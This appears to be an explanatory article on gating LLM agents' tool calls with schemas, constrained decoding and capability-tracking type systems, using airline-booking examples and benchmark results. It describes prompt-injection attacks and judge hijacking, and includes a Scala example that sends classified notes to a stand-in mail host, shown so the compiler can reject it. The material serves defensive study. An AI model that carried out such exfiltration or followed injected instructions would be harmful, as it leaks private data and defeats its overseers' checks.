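# Formal checks and type systems as gates on tool calls issued by language models

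## Tool calls and the gate between model and tool

A large language model produces text, so it needs other software to turn some of that text into actions such as canceling a flight, refunding a payment or searching a mailbox. Developers describe functions, called *tools*, to the model and specify a format for requesting them. A *tool call* is a request that contains a function's name and values for its arguments. An *agent* is a system in which a model works through a task by making tool calls.

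Software outside the model decides whether a call runs. In the simplest agents, this software runs every call it can parse. It could instead check each call against rules and refuse the ones that break them. Formal methods, the branch of computer science that uses logic to establish what a program can and cannot do, offer several ways to do this: type systems, constraint solvers, temporal logics, and plans verified in advance. They can catch different errors, and all of them depend on someone having translated the written rules into logic correctly.

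### The agent loop

Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, describe an agent as a loop in which the result of each tool call feeds into the model's next round of planning. Spelled out, one round goes like this:

1. A program, the host, assembles the model's input (its *context*): instructions, descriptions of the available tools, and the conversation so far.
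2. The model generates either a message to the user or a tool call.
3. If the output is a tool call, the host parses it and runs the function with those arguments.
4. The host appends the function's result to the context and starts the next round.

In *τ-bench*, a widely used test of customer-service agents, Yao, Shinn and colleagues (2024) implement every database action as a deterministic Python function. The model sees only the text that these functions return from the database, and it can change a record only by calling one of them. The call is a convenient place for a formal check because, although nobody can predict what the model will write, a call reaches the host as a small structured object and names a function with a definite effect.

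Take an airline that gives its agent the tool `cancel_reservation(reservation_id, reason)` and a short policy: the agent may cancel a reservation if the customer booked it within the last 24 hours, or if the airline has cancelled the flight. A customer writes that she booked this morning, her plans have changed, and she wants to cancel reservation K7QX2M. The model calls a lookup tool. The host runs it and returns the record, which gives a booking date 13 days in the past and a flight that is still on schedule. The model should now decline. Suppose it emits this instead:

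`cancel_reservation(reservation_id="K7QX2M", reason="change of plans")`

The host finds a function of that name and both arguments are strings, so it runs the function. The result, "cancelled", is added to the context, and the model tells the customer that the ticket has been cancelled. Every part of the loop has worked as designed, but the airline has cancelled a ticket against its own rules. The false claim about the date comes from a task in SASY's *Tau2 Airline Benchmark*, in which the simulated customer claims to have booked that morning but the record is 13 days old.

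The bad call was *well-formed*, meaning that it matched the tool's *schema*, the machine-readable description of the arguments, their types and their permitted values. A well-formed call can still violate the policy, and checking for this often requires information from outside the call, such as a database record or an earlier part of the conversation. A programmer can put some of these checks inside the tool. Yao and colleagues did this for part of their policy, so a call produces an error if its payment method is missing from the customer's profile. They left other rules to the agent, such as how many bags a customer must pay for, because human staff have the same freedom.

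### The gate and its three requirements

A *gate* is software outside the model that allows or refuses each tool call before it runs. It sits between steps 2 and 3 of the loop above.

The idea is half a century old. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported the work of a panel that advised the US Air Force on computers shared by people with different security clearances. The panel assumed that a legitimate user might be malicious and might run any program at all. Its answer was the *reference monitor*, which compares every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program with a list of what that user may do. Anderson set three requirements for any mechanism that implements it:

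- **It must be tamper-proof.** If a program can alter the mechanism, its verdicts are worth nothing.
- **The system must always invoke it.** Any program that escapes the check becomes part of the security apparatus, and then needs the same protection and analysis as the mechanism itself.
- **It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing.** Otherwise nobody has grounds for believing that it works in every case.

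Anderson described a Honeywell computer whose hardware confined each user's program to its own memory. The operating system suspended that confinement while it did work on the user's behalf, so the check did not always apply. Treating the whole operating system as the checking mechanism did not help, because it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse.

This design suits language models well because it does not rely on the controlled program behaving well. For the airline, "always invoked" means that the agent has no other route to the reservations database, such as a general command line. "Tamper-proof" means that the model can only propose calls. It cannot edit the rules or make a fact true by asserting it. As for size, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, wrote gate policies for retail, airline and telecom agents in Lean 4, a programming language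 that also supports proofs about programs. The three policies total 583 lines, excluding the code that fetches facts from the database. The guarantee assumes that those facts are accurate.

### Two test environments

Most of the evidence about gates comes from two families of tests, which measure different things.

τ-bench and its successor, *τ²-Bench* (Barres, Dong and colleagues, 2025), give the agent a written policy and a set of tools, while a second language model plays the customer. The airline domain has 50 tasks, 300 flights and 2,000 reservations. *τ²-Bench* adds a telecom domain in which the customer also has tools and can, for example, switch a phone's airplane mode on or off when the agent asks. In the retail and airline domains, a task counts as solved if the final database matches the one correct outcome and the agent has given the customer the information she needed.

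Yao and colleagues also introduced a measure of consistency, *pass^k*: the probability that all of *k* independent trials of a task succeed, averaged over tasks. If an agent runs a task *n* times and succeeds *c* times, the estimate is

$$\text{pass}^k = \mathbb{E}_{\text{task}}\left[\binom{c}{k} \Big/ \binom{n}{k}\right].$$

An agent that succeeds in three of four trials has a pass^1 of 0.75 on that task, a pass^2 of 3/6 = 0.5, and a pass^4 of zero. The better-known pass@k, the chance that *at least one* of *k* trials succeeds, rises rather than falls as *k* grows. Pass^k is more relevant for an airline that handles the same request thousands of times.

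An agent can complete a task while violating the policy. As Yao and colleagues acknowledge, an agent that cancels the right reservation without asking for the required confirmation still leaves the database in the correct state. The tasks have also changed over time, so scores from different years may not be comparable. *SEATauBench* (2026), an adaptation to Southeast Asian languages, uses corrected versions of the retail and airline tasks.

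The other family tests security. In a *prompt injection* attack, someone plants instructions in data that the agent will read, such as an email or a web page. The model receives instructions and data as one stream of text and has no formal way to tell them apart. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) simulates four workplaces (office software, Slack, travel booking and banking) with 97 user tasks. It pairs each user task with every attacker goal in the same workplace, which gives 629 security cases. The *attack success rate* is the share of those cases in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. The paper also reports *utility*, the share of user tasks that the agent completes, because an agent that did nothing would have an attack success rate of zero. A low rate can also reflect incompetence. In the 2024 experiments, more capable models were easier to attack because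 weaker ones often failed at the attacker's task too. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which *StepGuard* (2026) uses alongside AgentDojo, adds longer workflows and helpful third-party instructions, so a defence that blocks every outside instruction loses points there.

### The policy in the prompt, and the second model as judge

The easiest way to enforce a policy is to include it in the model's instructions, which takes no engineering. Instructions can also cover rules that can't be checked from tool calls, such as when to hand a customer over to a human. They can guide the model to the right action from the start, whereas a gate can only refuse a wrong one. Agents in τ²-bench already have the policy in their prompt, so a gate there supplements the prompt.

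The prompt is weak enforcement, though. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) tested an agent on the airline tasks using an openly released model with 26 billion parameters. Without a gate, 234 of the agent's 353 state-changing calls (66.3%) broke at least one encoded policy clause. A more permissive reading of one clause, about customer confirmation, lowers the figure to 36.8%. With a rule-based gate, 3 of 116 calls broke a clause. The gated agent also changed far fewer records but solved no fewer tasks, which suggests that the airline would not have wanted many of the missing calls. Llama-3.3-70B broke a clause in 86.9% of its calls without the gate. Neither model is among the strongest of 2026, and the rates for frontier models are probably lower.

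Another common safeguard is a second model acting as judge, which reads each proposed call, often with the conversation around it, and approves or blocks it. Its great strength is that it can assess meaning. Doshi and colleagues give the example of a calendar agent that moves a work meeting because it clashes with a medical appointment, then emails the user's coworkers and mentions what the appointment is for. A rule about argument types can't block that email, since the body is a valid string whatever it contains. A judge might catch it, though it might also fail to infer from a terse calendar title that the matter is private. Debenedetti and colleagues found that a separate attack detector cut the success rate of prompt injection attacks to 8%, from just under 25% for the best agents of 2024.

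A judge cannot give a guarantee. Doshi and colleagues point out that a persistent attacker may need only one success and can tailor the attack to the defence. The judge also reads text that the attacker may have written. Debenedetti and colleagues chose not to let a language model score their benchmark because an injection that hijacks the agent might also hijack the evaluator. Judges also make mistakes when no one is attacking them. When Sankar and colleagues audited the episodes that their judge had flagged, they found 18 cases in which it objected to switching on a customer's roaming although the system's records placed the phone line abroad. Using a judge also takes time. In Yu and colleagues' reimplementation of one such system, runs took 74% longer on average, while their rule-based gate decided in microseconds.

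*StepGuard* puts a judge where a gate would go, using a trained guard model to inspect calls before they run. Such a model can meet Anderson's requirement that the system always invoke the check. It does not meet his requirement that the check be completely analyzable, because nobody can yet establish how a neural network will respond to every input.

### Five kinds of bad call

The calls a rule-based gate can catch depend on the information available to it. Sankar and colleagues ran five Qwen models, from 0.8 to 27 billion parameters, on 278 τ²-bench tasks under two versions of their gate. The gate stopped 1,702 calls, which they sorted into five kinds.

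| Kind of bad call | Airline example | Stopped calls | What the check has to read |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invalid invocation | Calling `cancel_reservation` with no `reservation_id` | 551 | The call, the list of tools and their schemas |
| State incompatibility | Cancelling a flight that has already departed | 157 | The current database record |
| Temporal incompatibility | Cancelling before looking up the reservation | 411 | The history of earlier calls |
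| Authorization failure | Cancelling another customer's reservation, or cancelling without the customer's confirmation | 572 | Records of identity, ownership and consent |
| Policy prohibition | Cancelling a non-refundable ticket | 313 | The policy's own conditions and the facts they mention |

The five kinds overlap because a single call can break several rules at once, and their counts add up to 2,004. Another 72 stopped calls fall under none of the five. The gate's supporting software had failed on them, and the gate *fails closed*, meaning it blocks a call when a check breaks down or evidence is missing.

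Of the 551 invalid invocations, 534 named a tool that the agent did not have. Nearly all of these came from telecom agents trying to operate the customer's phone directly. The other 17 had arguments that failed the schema, so a gate that checked only arguments would have stopped 1% of the total. The call to cancel K7QX2M would pass that gate because it names a real tool and its arguments are valid. The flight has not left, the agent has looked up the record, and the customer owns the booking and asked for the cancellation herself. The call breaks only the 24-hour rule, and a gate needs the booking date, the current time and a formal version of the rule to detect that. In the study, 69 stopped calls broke the airline's cancellation rules.

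The proportions are not a reliable guide to agents in general. The two smallest models made 1,224 of the 1,702 calls, and many calls are repeats, because agents often sent the same request again after a refusal. Two rules stricter than the benchmark's own policy account for 164 of the temporal failures.

The frequency of bad calls is also a poor guide to harm. Sankar and colleagues replayed the episodes that had run without a gate to find calls that their rules would have stopped. They found 312 invalid invocations, none of which had changed any data, because a call to a missing tool fails by itself. At least 33 other calls had altered a record. Of these, 17 broke a temporal rule, 14 a rule about the current state and 3 a prohibition, with one call breaking two. The replay could not test whether customers had given consent, so the real number is probably higher.

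## Argument types and schemas

The simplest check a gate can make is whether a call is well-formed. This requires only the call, the list of tools and their schemas. Most models emit their calls as JSON, a text format that pairs names with values. Developers describe the arguments in JSON Schema, a language for specifying what JSON may contain. *JSONSchemaBench* (Geng, Cooper and colleagues, 2025) calls JSON Schema an industry-wide standard for constraining model output.

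### From bare strings to conditions between fields

A basic schema for `cancel_reservation` lists two strings:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "reservation_id": {"type": "string"},
    "reason": {"type": "string"}
  },
  "required": ["reservation_id", "reason"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

This schema rejects a call with no `reservation_id`, a call that gives the number 7 as its reason, and a call with an invented third argument such as `waive_fee`. Its last two lines are needed because JSON Schema otherwise treats every listed argument as optional and accepts unlisted ones. The schema still accepts any string as an ID, so `reservation_id="the Boston flight"` passes.

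The developer can tighten this step by step. Suppose the airline adds two optional arguments, `details` and a numeric `refund_amount`.

| Refinement | In JSON Schema | What it newly excludes |
|---|---|---|
| Pattern for `reservation_id` | `"pattern": "^[A-Z0-9]{6}$"` | "the Boston flight", "k7qx2m", an empty string |
| Enumeration for `reason` | `"enum": ["change of plan", "airline cancelled", "other"]` | "medical", "customer is upset" |
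| Range for `refund_amount` | `"exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximum": 10000` | A refund of −50, or of 31,240 when the model dropped the decimal point from 312.40 |
| Condition between fields | `"if": {"properties": {"reason": {"const": "other"}}}, "then": {"required": ["details"]}` | The reason "other" with no explanation |

A pattern constrains only the shape of a string. This one admits 36⁶ codes, about 2.2 billion, while the airline in τ²-bench has 2,000 reservations, so nearly every code that passes belongs to no reservation. The enumeration in the schema now rejects the call to cancel K7QX2M because the model gave the reason as "change of plans" instead of "change of plan". Once the model removes the final *s*, the call passes, even though the booking is 13 days old and the policy forbids the cancellation.

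### Types that depend on a record

Programming-language researchers call a type with a condition attached a *refinement type*. A sensible type for the refund is

$$\{\, a : \text{number} \mid 0 < a \le \text{paid}(r) \,\},$$

which means any number *a* that is greater than zero and no larger than the amount paid for reservation *r*. The lower bound is easy, since zero is a constant and JSON Schema can compare a value with a constant. The upper bound is in the airline's database, and it changes with the reservation that the model names in the same call. The host could look up the reservation beforehand and write its price into a fresh schema, but then it must know which reservation the model will choose, and the record could change in the meantime. It is usually simpler to wait for the complete call and then look up the record.

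Many rules about arguments depend on data outside the call. Sankar and colleagues give the example of an account that has spent 60 units of a budget of 100. A payment of 40 is acceptable and a payment of 70 is too large, but the limit changes with every purchase. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) encodes a rule from τ-bench's retail policy that a refund must go to the original payment method or to an existing gift card. The encoded condition checks the database to see whether the payment method matches the order. For gift cards, it only tests whether the argument contains the text "gift_card", which needs no lookup but doesn't establish that the customer has such a card.

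### Checking afterwards, or masking during generation

A host can enforce a schema after the model has finished generating a call. It parses the call, runs a validator, and returns an error if the call is invalid. This works with any model, and the same code can also check conditions that need a database. The drawback is that the model has to generate a failed call again.

The alternative is *constrained generation*, which prevents the model from writing an invalid call at all. A model produces text one *token* at a time, a token being a word or a fragment of one. At each step it computes a score, called a logit, for every token in its vocabulary, and a function called softmax turns the scores into probabilities. Constrained generation changes the scores just before softmax. Based on the accounts by Geng and colleagues and by Li, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *XGrammar-2*, it works like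 this:

1. An engine compiles the schema into a grammar, from which it can determine how any partial output may continue.
2. The engine finds its place in the grammar, given the output so far.
3. It computes a *mask*, which marks every token that could still lead to a valid output.
4. The model computes its logits as usual.
5. The engine sets the logit of every other token to minus infinity, which gives that token a probability of zero.
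6. The software picks one of the remaining tokens, appends it to the output, and returns to step 2. It stops when the model emits an end marker, which the mask permits only once the output is complete.

If *M* is the set of permitted tokens and *p(t)* the model's own probability for token *t*, the new probability of a permitted token is

$$p'(t) = \frac{p(t)}{\sum_{u \in M} p(u)}.$$

Suppose the model has written `{"reservation_id": "K7Q`. The pattern requires three more capitals or digits. The engine permits the tokens `X`, `X2` and `X2M`, and masks `x2m`, the hyphen and the closing quotation mark. After the sixth character, the engine permits only the closing quotation mark.

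An agent complicates this because the right schema depends on which tool the model picks. Li and colleagues let the model write freely until it produces a tag containing a tool's name. The engine then switches to the grammar for that tool's arguments and returns to free text once the call is complete.

Masking requires access to the logits. Kamath and colleagues had to resample entire calls with closed models because, they note, commercial providers do not expose the next-token probabilities for the whole vocabulary. A developer who wants masking with a closed model therefore depends on the provider to offer it.

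### How well the engines work

Masking guarantees a valid output only if the engine translates the schema into a grammar correctly and no length limit cuts the output short. Geng and colleagues tested six engines on about 10,000 schemas that people had written for real software. They also tested the four open-source engines on the official JSON Schema test suite, which covers 45 categories of features. They call an engine *over-constrained* if it blocks outputs that the schema allows, and *under-constrained* if it lets through outputs that the schema forbids. Among the open-source engines, XGrammar was under-constrained in 38 categories and failed to compile at least one schema in three. Guidance was under-constrained in only one category but failed to compile at least one schema in 25. These results are for versions from early 2025, and both engines have probably improved since.

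For a gate, failing to compile a schema is a better error than under-constraining the output, because the developer finds out before the agent runs. An under-constrained engine produces invalid calls that are presented as guaranteed valid. Validating the finished call is worthwhile even when an engine has masked tokens during generation, because the check takes little work and means the gate does not have to trust the engine. Engines also vary somewhat on the same schema. JSON Schema does not define where whitespace may appear, and *Earley-Driven Dynamic Pruning for Efficient Structured Decoding* (2025) points out that different libraries can therefore produce different outputs from one model.

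With the better engines, speed is no longer a good reason to avoid masking. Geng and colleagues ran Llama-3.1-8B on schemas for function calls. The model took 15.4 milliseconds per token without constraints, about 30 with two of the engines, and 6.4 with Guidance. Guidance was faster because it skips the model wherever the grammar allows only one continuation, such as the name of a required argument.

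Compiling the grammar can take longer than using it. Chavan (2026), in *Constrained Decoding Eliminates Structural Failures in Small LLMs*, measured 4 to 8 milliseconds per schema for XGrammar and averages of 2.0 to 4.9 seconds for Outlines, an older engine. Li and colleagues report more than a second for XGrammar, probably because they compiled grammars for agents with many tools, while Chavan compiled one schema at a time. If every request has its own selection of tools, the engine can't reuse a complete grammar from an earlier request. XGrammar-2, Li and colleagues' successor to XGrammar, reuses the parts that recur and takes about 10 milliseconds. In their own tests, it added at most 6% to the time of an unconstrained run.

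### What strict modes promise

Model providers offer constrained generation as a "strict" or "structured" mode. OpenAI's earlier JSON mode guaranteed only that the output was valid JSON, so it allowed arguments that did not match the tool's schema, such as `{"banana": 3}`. In August 2024, OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* promised that outputs would "exactly match" the developer's schema. Developers turn this on for tool calls with `strict: true`. OpenAI reported that a new model with this mode followed complex schemas 100% of the time, compared with less than 40% for a model from 2023. It credits both masking and extra training, so the comparison does not isolate the effect of masking. OpenAI's current guide, *Structured Outputs*, recommends the feature over JSON mode wherever possible.

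The promise applies only to schemas that the provider accepts. At the launch, the developer Simon Willison noted that OpenAI supported only a subset of JSON Schema, prohibited extra properties, and required the model to fill in every listed field. An optional `refund_amount` therefore has to become a required field that may be null. A few months later, Geng and colleagues found that OpenAI accepted 89% of 1,707 schemas for function calls and Google's Gemini accepted 86%, and that every output they produced was valid. Of GitHub schemas with 10 to 30 fields, OpenAI accepted 30% and Gemini 8%. Both providers had apparently chosen to support few features and enforce them reliably. These percentages are from early 2025 and are a poor guide to what either provider accepts now.

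Strict modes make no promise about whether the values are true, or whether the airline's policy permits the call.

### Valid calls that are wrong

Li and colleagues measured validity and correctness on BFCL-v3, a public test of function calling. On that test, a correct call must satisfy the schema and be the right call for the request.

| Model | Valid, unmasked | Valid, masked | Correct, unmasked | Correct, masked |
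|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3.2-1B | 22.1% | 100% | 6.1% | 32.8% |
| Llama-3.2-3B | 40.7% | 100% | 33.1% | 77.8% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 67.0% | 100% | 59.5% | 80.9% |
| Llama-3.1-70B | 51.9% | 100% | 45.6% | 86.4% |

Masking helped every model a great deal, but it also made many wrong calls valid. For the smallest model, the share of valid calls rose by 78 percentage points and the share of correct ones by 27, so roughly two-thirds of the calls that masking repaired were still wrong. For the largest model, the gains were 48 and 41 points, which suggests that most of its repaired calls had been wrong only in format.

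In Chavan's small experiment, with 14 tasks and five models of up to 4 billion parameters, masking corrected some errors but not others. Two of the models wrote the prices on a receipt as text, for instance "$4.98" with the dollar sign, where the schema required a number. Masking allowed them to write only numbers, and the numbers were right. Another task required a web search followed by an email. Qwen3-0.6B called only the search tool, with or without masking, because the schema accepted a list with one call. Llama-3.2-1B made both calls under masking, but the body of its email read "1. 2. 3. 4. 5."

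Larger and newer models rarely break a schema, but they still fill in wrong values. *The Structured Output Benchmark* (Singh, Khurdula et al., 2026) tested 21 models on extracting facts from a text into a given schema. GPT-5.4's output passed the schema 99.3% of the time, and 79.8% of its values exactly matched the reference answer. Exact matching is a harsh measure, since it counts "United States" as wrong where the reference has "American", and extracting facts from documents isn't the same as calling tools. The company behind the benchmark also has a model in the ranking. Still, the gap between the two numbers is too wide for scoring rules alone to explain, and no schema check would have detected it.

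Studies disagree on whether masking itself makes answers worse. Geng and colleagues tested Llama-3.1-8B on three reasoning tasks, and it did at least as well with every engine as it did without constraints. On grade-school mathematics, accuracy rose from 80.1% to between 81.6% and 83.8%. They also cite earlier work that found a loss, and a reply that blamed the loss on poor prompts and badly designed schemas. *Token-Oriented Object Notation vs JSON* (2026) reports gains for weaker models, but the accuracy of one large model, Hermes-4-405B, fell from 92.5% in plain JSON to 35.0% with constrained output. The effect seems to depend heavily on the model and format, so developers should measure it before relying on either result.

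A schema meant for an agent's final answer can prevent the agent from calling tools at all. *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) explains that if the developer leaves the schema active throughout the run, the mask can block the tags that open a tool call.

### How a mask can produce a false argument

Suppose the customer wants to cancel because she is ill. The model is about to fill in `reason`, and without a mask it would give these probabilities to the possible values:

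| Value | Model's probability | In the schema? | Probability after renormalising |
|---|---|---|---|
| medical | 0.70 | No | 0 |
| airline cancelled | 0.15 | Yes | 0.15 / 0.30 = 50% |
| other | 0.10 | Yes | 0.10 / 0.30 = 33% |
| change of plan | 0.05 | Yes | 0.05 / 0.30 = 17% |

With "medical" gone, the other three values share its probability in proportion to their own. The claim that the airline cancelled the flight, which the model gave a probability of 15%, is now the most likely output, so software that always picks the most likely value will pick it. The resulting call is valid, but the reason it gives is false. Because the airline's policy permits a cancellation when the airline has cancelled the flight, a gate that relied on the reason in the call would let it through. The gate needs to look up the flight's status instead.

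The table renormalises over whole values, whereas a real engine works token by token. The two methods agree if every value begins with a different token, but they can differ a lot if a forbidden value shares its beginning with a permitted one. Suppose the model's most probable value is "change of health" instead of "medical", again with a probability of 0.70. The token "change" then has a probability of 0.75 (0.70 for "change of health" plus 0.05 for "change of plan"). The engine permits this token because it could lead to "change of plan". Two tokens later it masks "health", leaving only "plan". The agent therefore outputs "change of plan" 75% of the time, whereas renormalising over whole values would give 17%.

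The engine goes wrong because it checks only whether a token *could* lead to a valid output. To match the whole-value result, it would have to weight each token by the probability that the model would go on to produce a valid output, which requires looking ahead through every continuation. Singh and colleagues cite work from 2024 that found the same distortion in practice. Masking can also corrupt numbers. In a hypothetical case from Geng and colleagues, a model is about to write "89,000" where the schema permits only digits. The mask blocks the comma and the model continues with an extra zero, which gives 890000. A refund with that error would be ten times too large, and only an upper bound on the amount would stop it.

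No list of reasons will ever be complete, so adding "medical" would be only a partial fix. A value such as "unknown" lets the model avoid giving a false reason. The developer has to describe this value in the tool's instructions, because masking only rescales the probabilities that the model already assigns, and a value with zero probability stays at zero. The model should also be free not to call the tool, so that it can ask the customer what happened. Settings that force a tool call remove this option, as does a required field that can't be null.

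Some remedies delay masking. *Thinking Before Constraining* (2026) lets the model reason in ordinary text until it emits a trigger token, then applies the schema. *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs* (2026) has the model write an unconstrained draft, then generate the constrained version with the draft in its context. Both should help when a model can produce the right answer but gets the format wrong, though neither lets it output a value that the schema doesn't allow.

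There is a good case for not masking enumerations like this one, because masking hides the fact that a value is missing from the list. If the host validates the call afterwards instead, the call with "medical" fails, the model receives an error that lists the permitted reasons, and the developer finds the missing value in the logs.

### How much a schema check catches

Sankar and colleagues' gate stopped 1,702 calls on τ²-bench, of which just 17 had arguments that failed the tool's schema. Another 252 had arguments that satisfied the schema but broke a rule. Many of these tried to send a refund to a payment method other than the one used for the order. Such an argument is an ordinary string, and only the order's record shows that it is wrong.

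A grammar that listed the permitted tool names would also have prevented the 534 calls to tools that the agents did not have. But it would not necessarily have led the telecom agents to the right step, which was to ask the customer to operate the phone. Once a model has begun a tool call, it has to finish with a permitted name, even if none of the permitted tools is appropriate. The same kind of constraint produced the false claim that the airline had cancelled the ill customer's flight.

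The figure of 17 comes from favourable conditions. The agents had 43 tools in total, with at most 16 in any one domain. Most arguments are short strings. The Qwen models are recent and τ²-bench is public, so the models' training data may have included similar tools.

Without masking, between a third and three-quarters of the Llama models' calls on BFCL-v3 were invalid. The 70-billion-parameter model did worse than the 8-billion one, which suggests that familiarity with the expected format matters more than general ability. Schema size also matters. When Geng and colleagues had Llama-3.2-1B write JSON without constraints, it produced valid output for 90% of the function-call schemas but 13% of the GitHub schemas with 100 to 500 fields.

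Sankar and colleagues also ran their gate on DTap, a collection of simulated applications for testing attacks on agents. In six of these applications, with 177 tools, 58% of the calls that the gate stopped during attacks were invalid invocations. That number isn't comparable with the 17, because the DTap category also includes unknown tools and some calls that failed balance and budget checks. The agents on DTap were also under attack and ran without the extended reasoning they had on τ²-bench.

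Llama's failures came from 2024 models, and GPT-5.4's pass rate of 99.3% suggests that a strong current model will seldom fail an ordinary schema, even without masking. For an airline with 14 tools and such a model, the schema check would probably stop very few calls. An agent that writes configuration files with hundreds of fields, or that is given new tools with every request, may well need the check far more often.

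## Type systems for programs that call tools

Instead of emitting one call at a time, a model can write a short program that calls several tools as functions. A compiler checks the whole program, and the host runs it only if the compiler accepts it. For the airline, the model might write this in Scala, a language whose compiler works out the type of every expression before the program runs:

```scala
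val r = getReservationDetails("K7QX2M")
val leg = r.flights.head
val status = getFlightStatus(leg.flightNumber, leg.date)
if status == "cancelled" then
  cancelReservation(r.reservationId, "airline cancelled")
else
  println("The flight is still on schedule.")
```

The compiler can follow results from one call to the next. If the model had passed `r`, the whole record, to `cancelReservation`, the compiler would reject the program because that function expects a string. It also checks both branches, though only one will run. With a suitable type system, it can work out which effects a piece of code may have, such as writing a file or sending data over a network.

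Ordinary types don't force the model to check the flight, though. A program that consists only of the call to `cancelReservation` also compiles.

### Capabilities and capture checking

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) present TACIT, a server that compiles and runs Scala programs written by agents. TACIT relies on *capabilities*, which are unforgeable values that a program must hold to perform particular actions. For example, a program can contact a host only if it holds a `Network` capability that covers that host.

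Operating systems have used capabilities since the 1960s, but they check capabilities while programs run. Scala 3 has an experimental feature, *capture checking*, that tracks them in types. Each type carries a *capture set*, which lists the capabilities a value of that type might reach. A logger that writes to the file `out` has the type `Logger^{out}`. A function from strings to strings that uses the network capability `net` has the type `String ->{net} String`. With a plain arrow, `String -> String`, the capture set is empty and the function is *pure*, which means it can compute a result but can't print, write a file or send anything.

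A value with a smaller capture set can stand in for one with a larger set, but not the other way round:

$$C_1 \subseteq C_2 \;\Rightarrow\; T^{C_1} <: T^{C_2},$$

where $<:$ means "can be used as".

TACIT puts private data in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's program cannot take the data out, but it can call `map`, which applies a function to the contents and wraps the result again. `map` accepts only pure functions.

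Suppose the airline keeps medical notes on passengers, and an attacker has persuaded the model to send them to a mail server:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/airline") {
  requestNetwork(Set("mail.example.com")) {
    val notes = readClassified("/airline/private/K7QX2M.txt")
    notes.map(text => text.length)
    notes.map(text => httpPost("https://mail.example.com", text))
  }
}
```

The compiler works through it as follows:

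1. `readClassified` returns a `Classified[String]`, so the program never holds the notes as an ordinary string.
2. `map` requires a function of type `String -> U`, where `U` can be any result type.
3. The first function computes a length. Its type is `String -> Int`, so this line is fine.
4. The second function calls `httpPost`, whose signature requires a `Network` capability. If `net` is the capability that `requestNetwork` granted, the function has the type `String ->{net} String`.
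5. The set {`net`} is not a subset of the empty set, so the types don't match and the compiler rejects the whole program.

The airline allowed this program to read the file and to contact the mail server, so a gate that checked each call separately could have let both through. The violation is the flow of information from one call to the other. The check is also conservative, so the compiler would reject the program even if `httpPost` were in a branch that never runs.

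The model could try other ways to get the text out. Printing it also requires a capability. The compiler tracks changes to variables, so the function can't save the text for later use. The function can't keep the network capability after the block ends either, because the type of the block's result can't mention that capability. A setting called *safe mode* forbids unchecked casts and reflection, which could let code use a capability without the compiler tracking it. Exceptions are harder to exclude because any division by zero can raise one, so TACIT catches them at run time and hides their messages.

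If the program prints a classified value, the agent receives `Classified(****)`, while the user's terminal shows the contents. When a task requires reading the text, the program can pass it to a second, trusted model, whose answer is also wrapped as a classified value.

Capabilities could also enforce the airline's cancellation policy. The airline would replace `cancelReservation` with a function that looks up the record and returns a capability to cancel that reservation only if the policy allows it. A program that skipped the check would not compile. Odersky and colleagues leave such run-time checks to future work. In their version of τ²-bench, `cancelReservation` takes a plain string, so the compiler would accept the forbidden cancellation of K7QX2M.

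### TACIT's security and task performance

To test security, Odersky and colleagues set up a software project with a folder of API keys and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Another 11 prompts asked for secrets directly or impersonated someone with authority. Each trial ran once with the wrapper and once with the secrets as plain strings. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

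| Model | Trials | Secure, wrapped | Secure, plain |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |

The perfect scores are expected from the design, so they mainly show that the implementation works. The injections were a weak test, since only three succeeded even without the wrapper. Most of the difference comes from 11 malicious requests, 8 of which extracted secrets from MiniMax when the wrapper was off.

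The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. On the 120 ordinary trials, Sonnet succeeded in 99.2% with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax succeeded in 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Sonnet's improvement may be an artifact, because without the wrapper Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

On τ²-bench, the comparison was between ordinary tool calls and Scala programs, averaged over ten runs of each task:

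| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Odersky and colleagues attribute the small but consistent gains to structured return values and helpful compiler errors. On 300 real software bugs from SWE-bench Lite, however, MiniMax's success rate fell from 43.3% to 41.7%, a difference of five bugs. On τ²-bench, at most 8% of the programs needed a retry.

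### Typed holes

In TACIT, the agent runs as usual and sends programs to a compiler. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, who overlap with the TACIT team, put the request to the model inside a program instead:

```scala
val r: Reservation = agent("find the customer's Boston booking")
```

The call to `agent` is a *typed hole*, a gap that the model must fill with code that produces a value of a required type, here `Reservation`. When execution reaches the hole, the runtime sends the model the task, the required type, the surrounding code and a list of the available variables. The model writes code, and the compiler checks it as if a developer had written it there. If the check fails, the model gets the compiler's errors and tries again, up to a fixed number of attempts. The new code can contain further holes, each with its own type.

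The generated code can use only the names available at the hole, so a developer grants a tool by making it available there. If `getReservationDetails` is available and `cancelReservation` is not, the model can look up bookings but can't cancel them. This protection depends on how sparingly the developer grants tools.

LACUNA runs none of the code if the compiler finds any error. Suppose a program cancels a reservation and then misspells the name of the function that books a replacement. Python would cancel the reservation before reporting the error, but with LACUNA the customer keeps her original ticket. This protects only against errors that the compiler can find, so if the function name is correct but the new flight is full, the program will already have cancelled the old ticket when the booking fails.

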